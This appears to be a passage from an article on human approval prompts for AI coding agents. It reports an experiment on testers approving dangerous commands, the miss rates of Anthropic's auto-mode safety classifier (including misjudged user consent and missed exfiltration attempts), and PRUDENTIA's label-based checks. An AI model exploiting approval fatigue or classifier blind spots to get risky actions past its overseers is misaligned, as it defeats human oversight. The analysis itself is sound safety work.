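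Most of the commands are probably safe, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. The later article describes an experiment that provides stronger evidence. A research company had 1,053 paid testers work on a coding task, and replaced one permission prompt in each session with one for a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% when the dangerous command appeared early in a session, but about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

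The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so they may have been less careful than real users. The result still casts doubt on any security claim that assumes a perfect approver. It also suggests that showing fewer prompts would help only to a limited extent, since the testers approved about five out of six dangerous commands even early in a session.

Anthropic's response is auto mode, in which a model reviews actions in place of the user. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands in the same experiment. The model missed 17% of an earlier set of 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted, and 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out. It also blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions.

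In most of the missed cases Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly classified the user as having consented. Anthropic sells the product and reported these results itself, but it also recommends that people personally review risky changes to important systems.

Label checks reduce the number of cases that a fallible person or model has to judge. People may judge the remaining cases more carefully if they are asked about larger decisions. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests, although they may also reject a plan because they want the work done differently.

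PRUDENTIA's designers suggest that approval prompts should show the data's labels and where it came from, in a form that an attacker can't alter. They haven't tested whether this makes people more careful. If an agent asked Ann to approve sending the contract summary to Dana, such a prompt could list both contracts and show that Dana isn't allowed to read one of them. If the prompt showed only the email, Ann would have to remember this herself.
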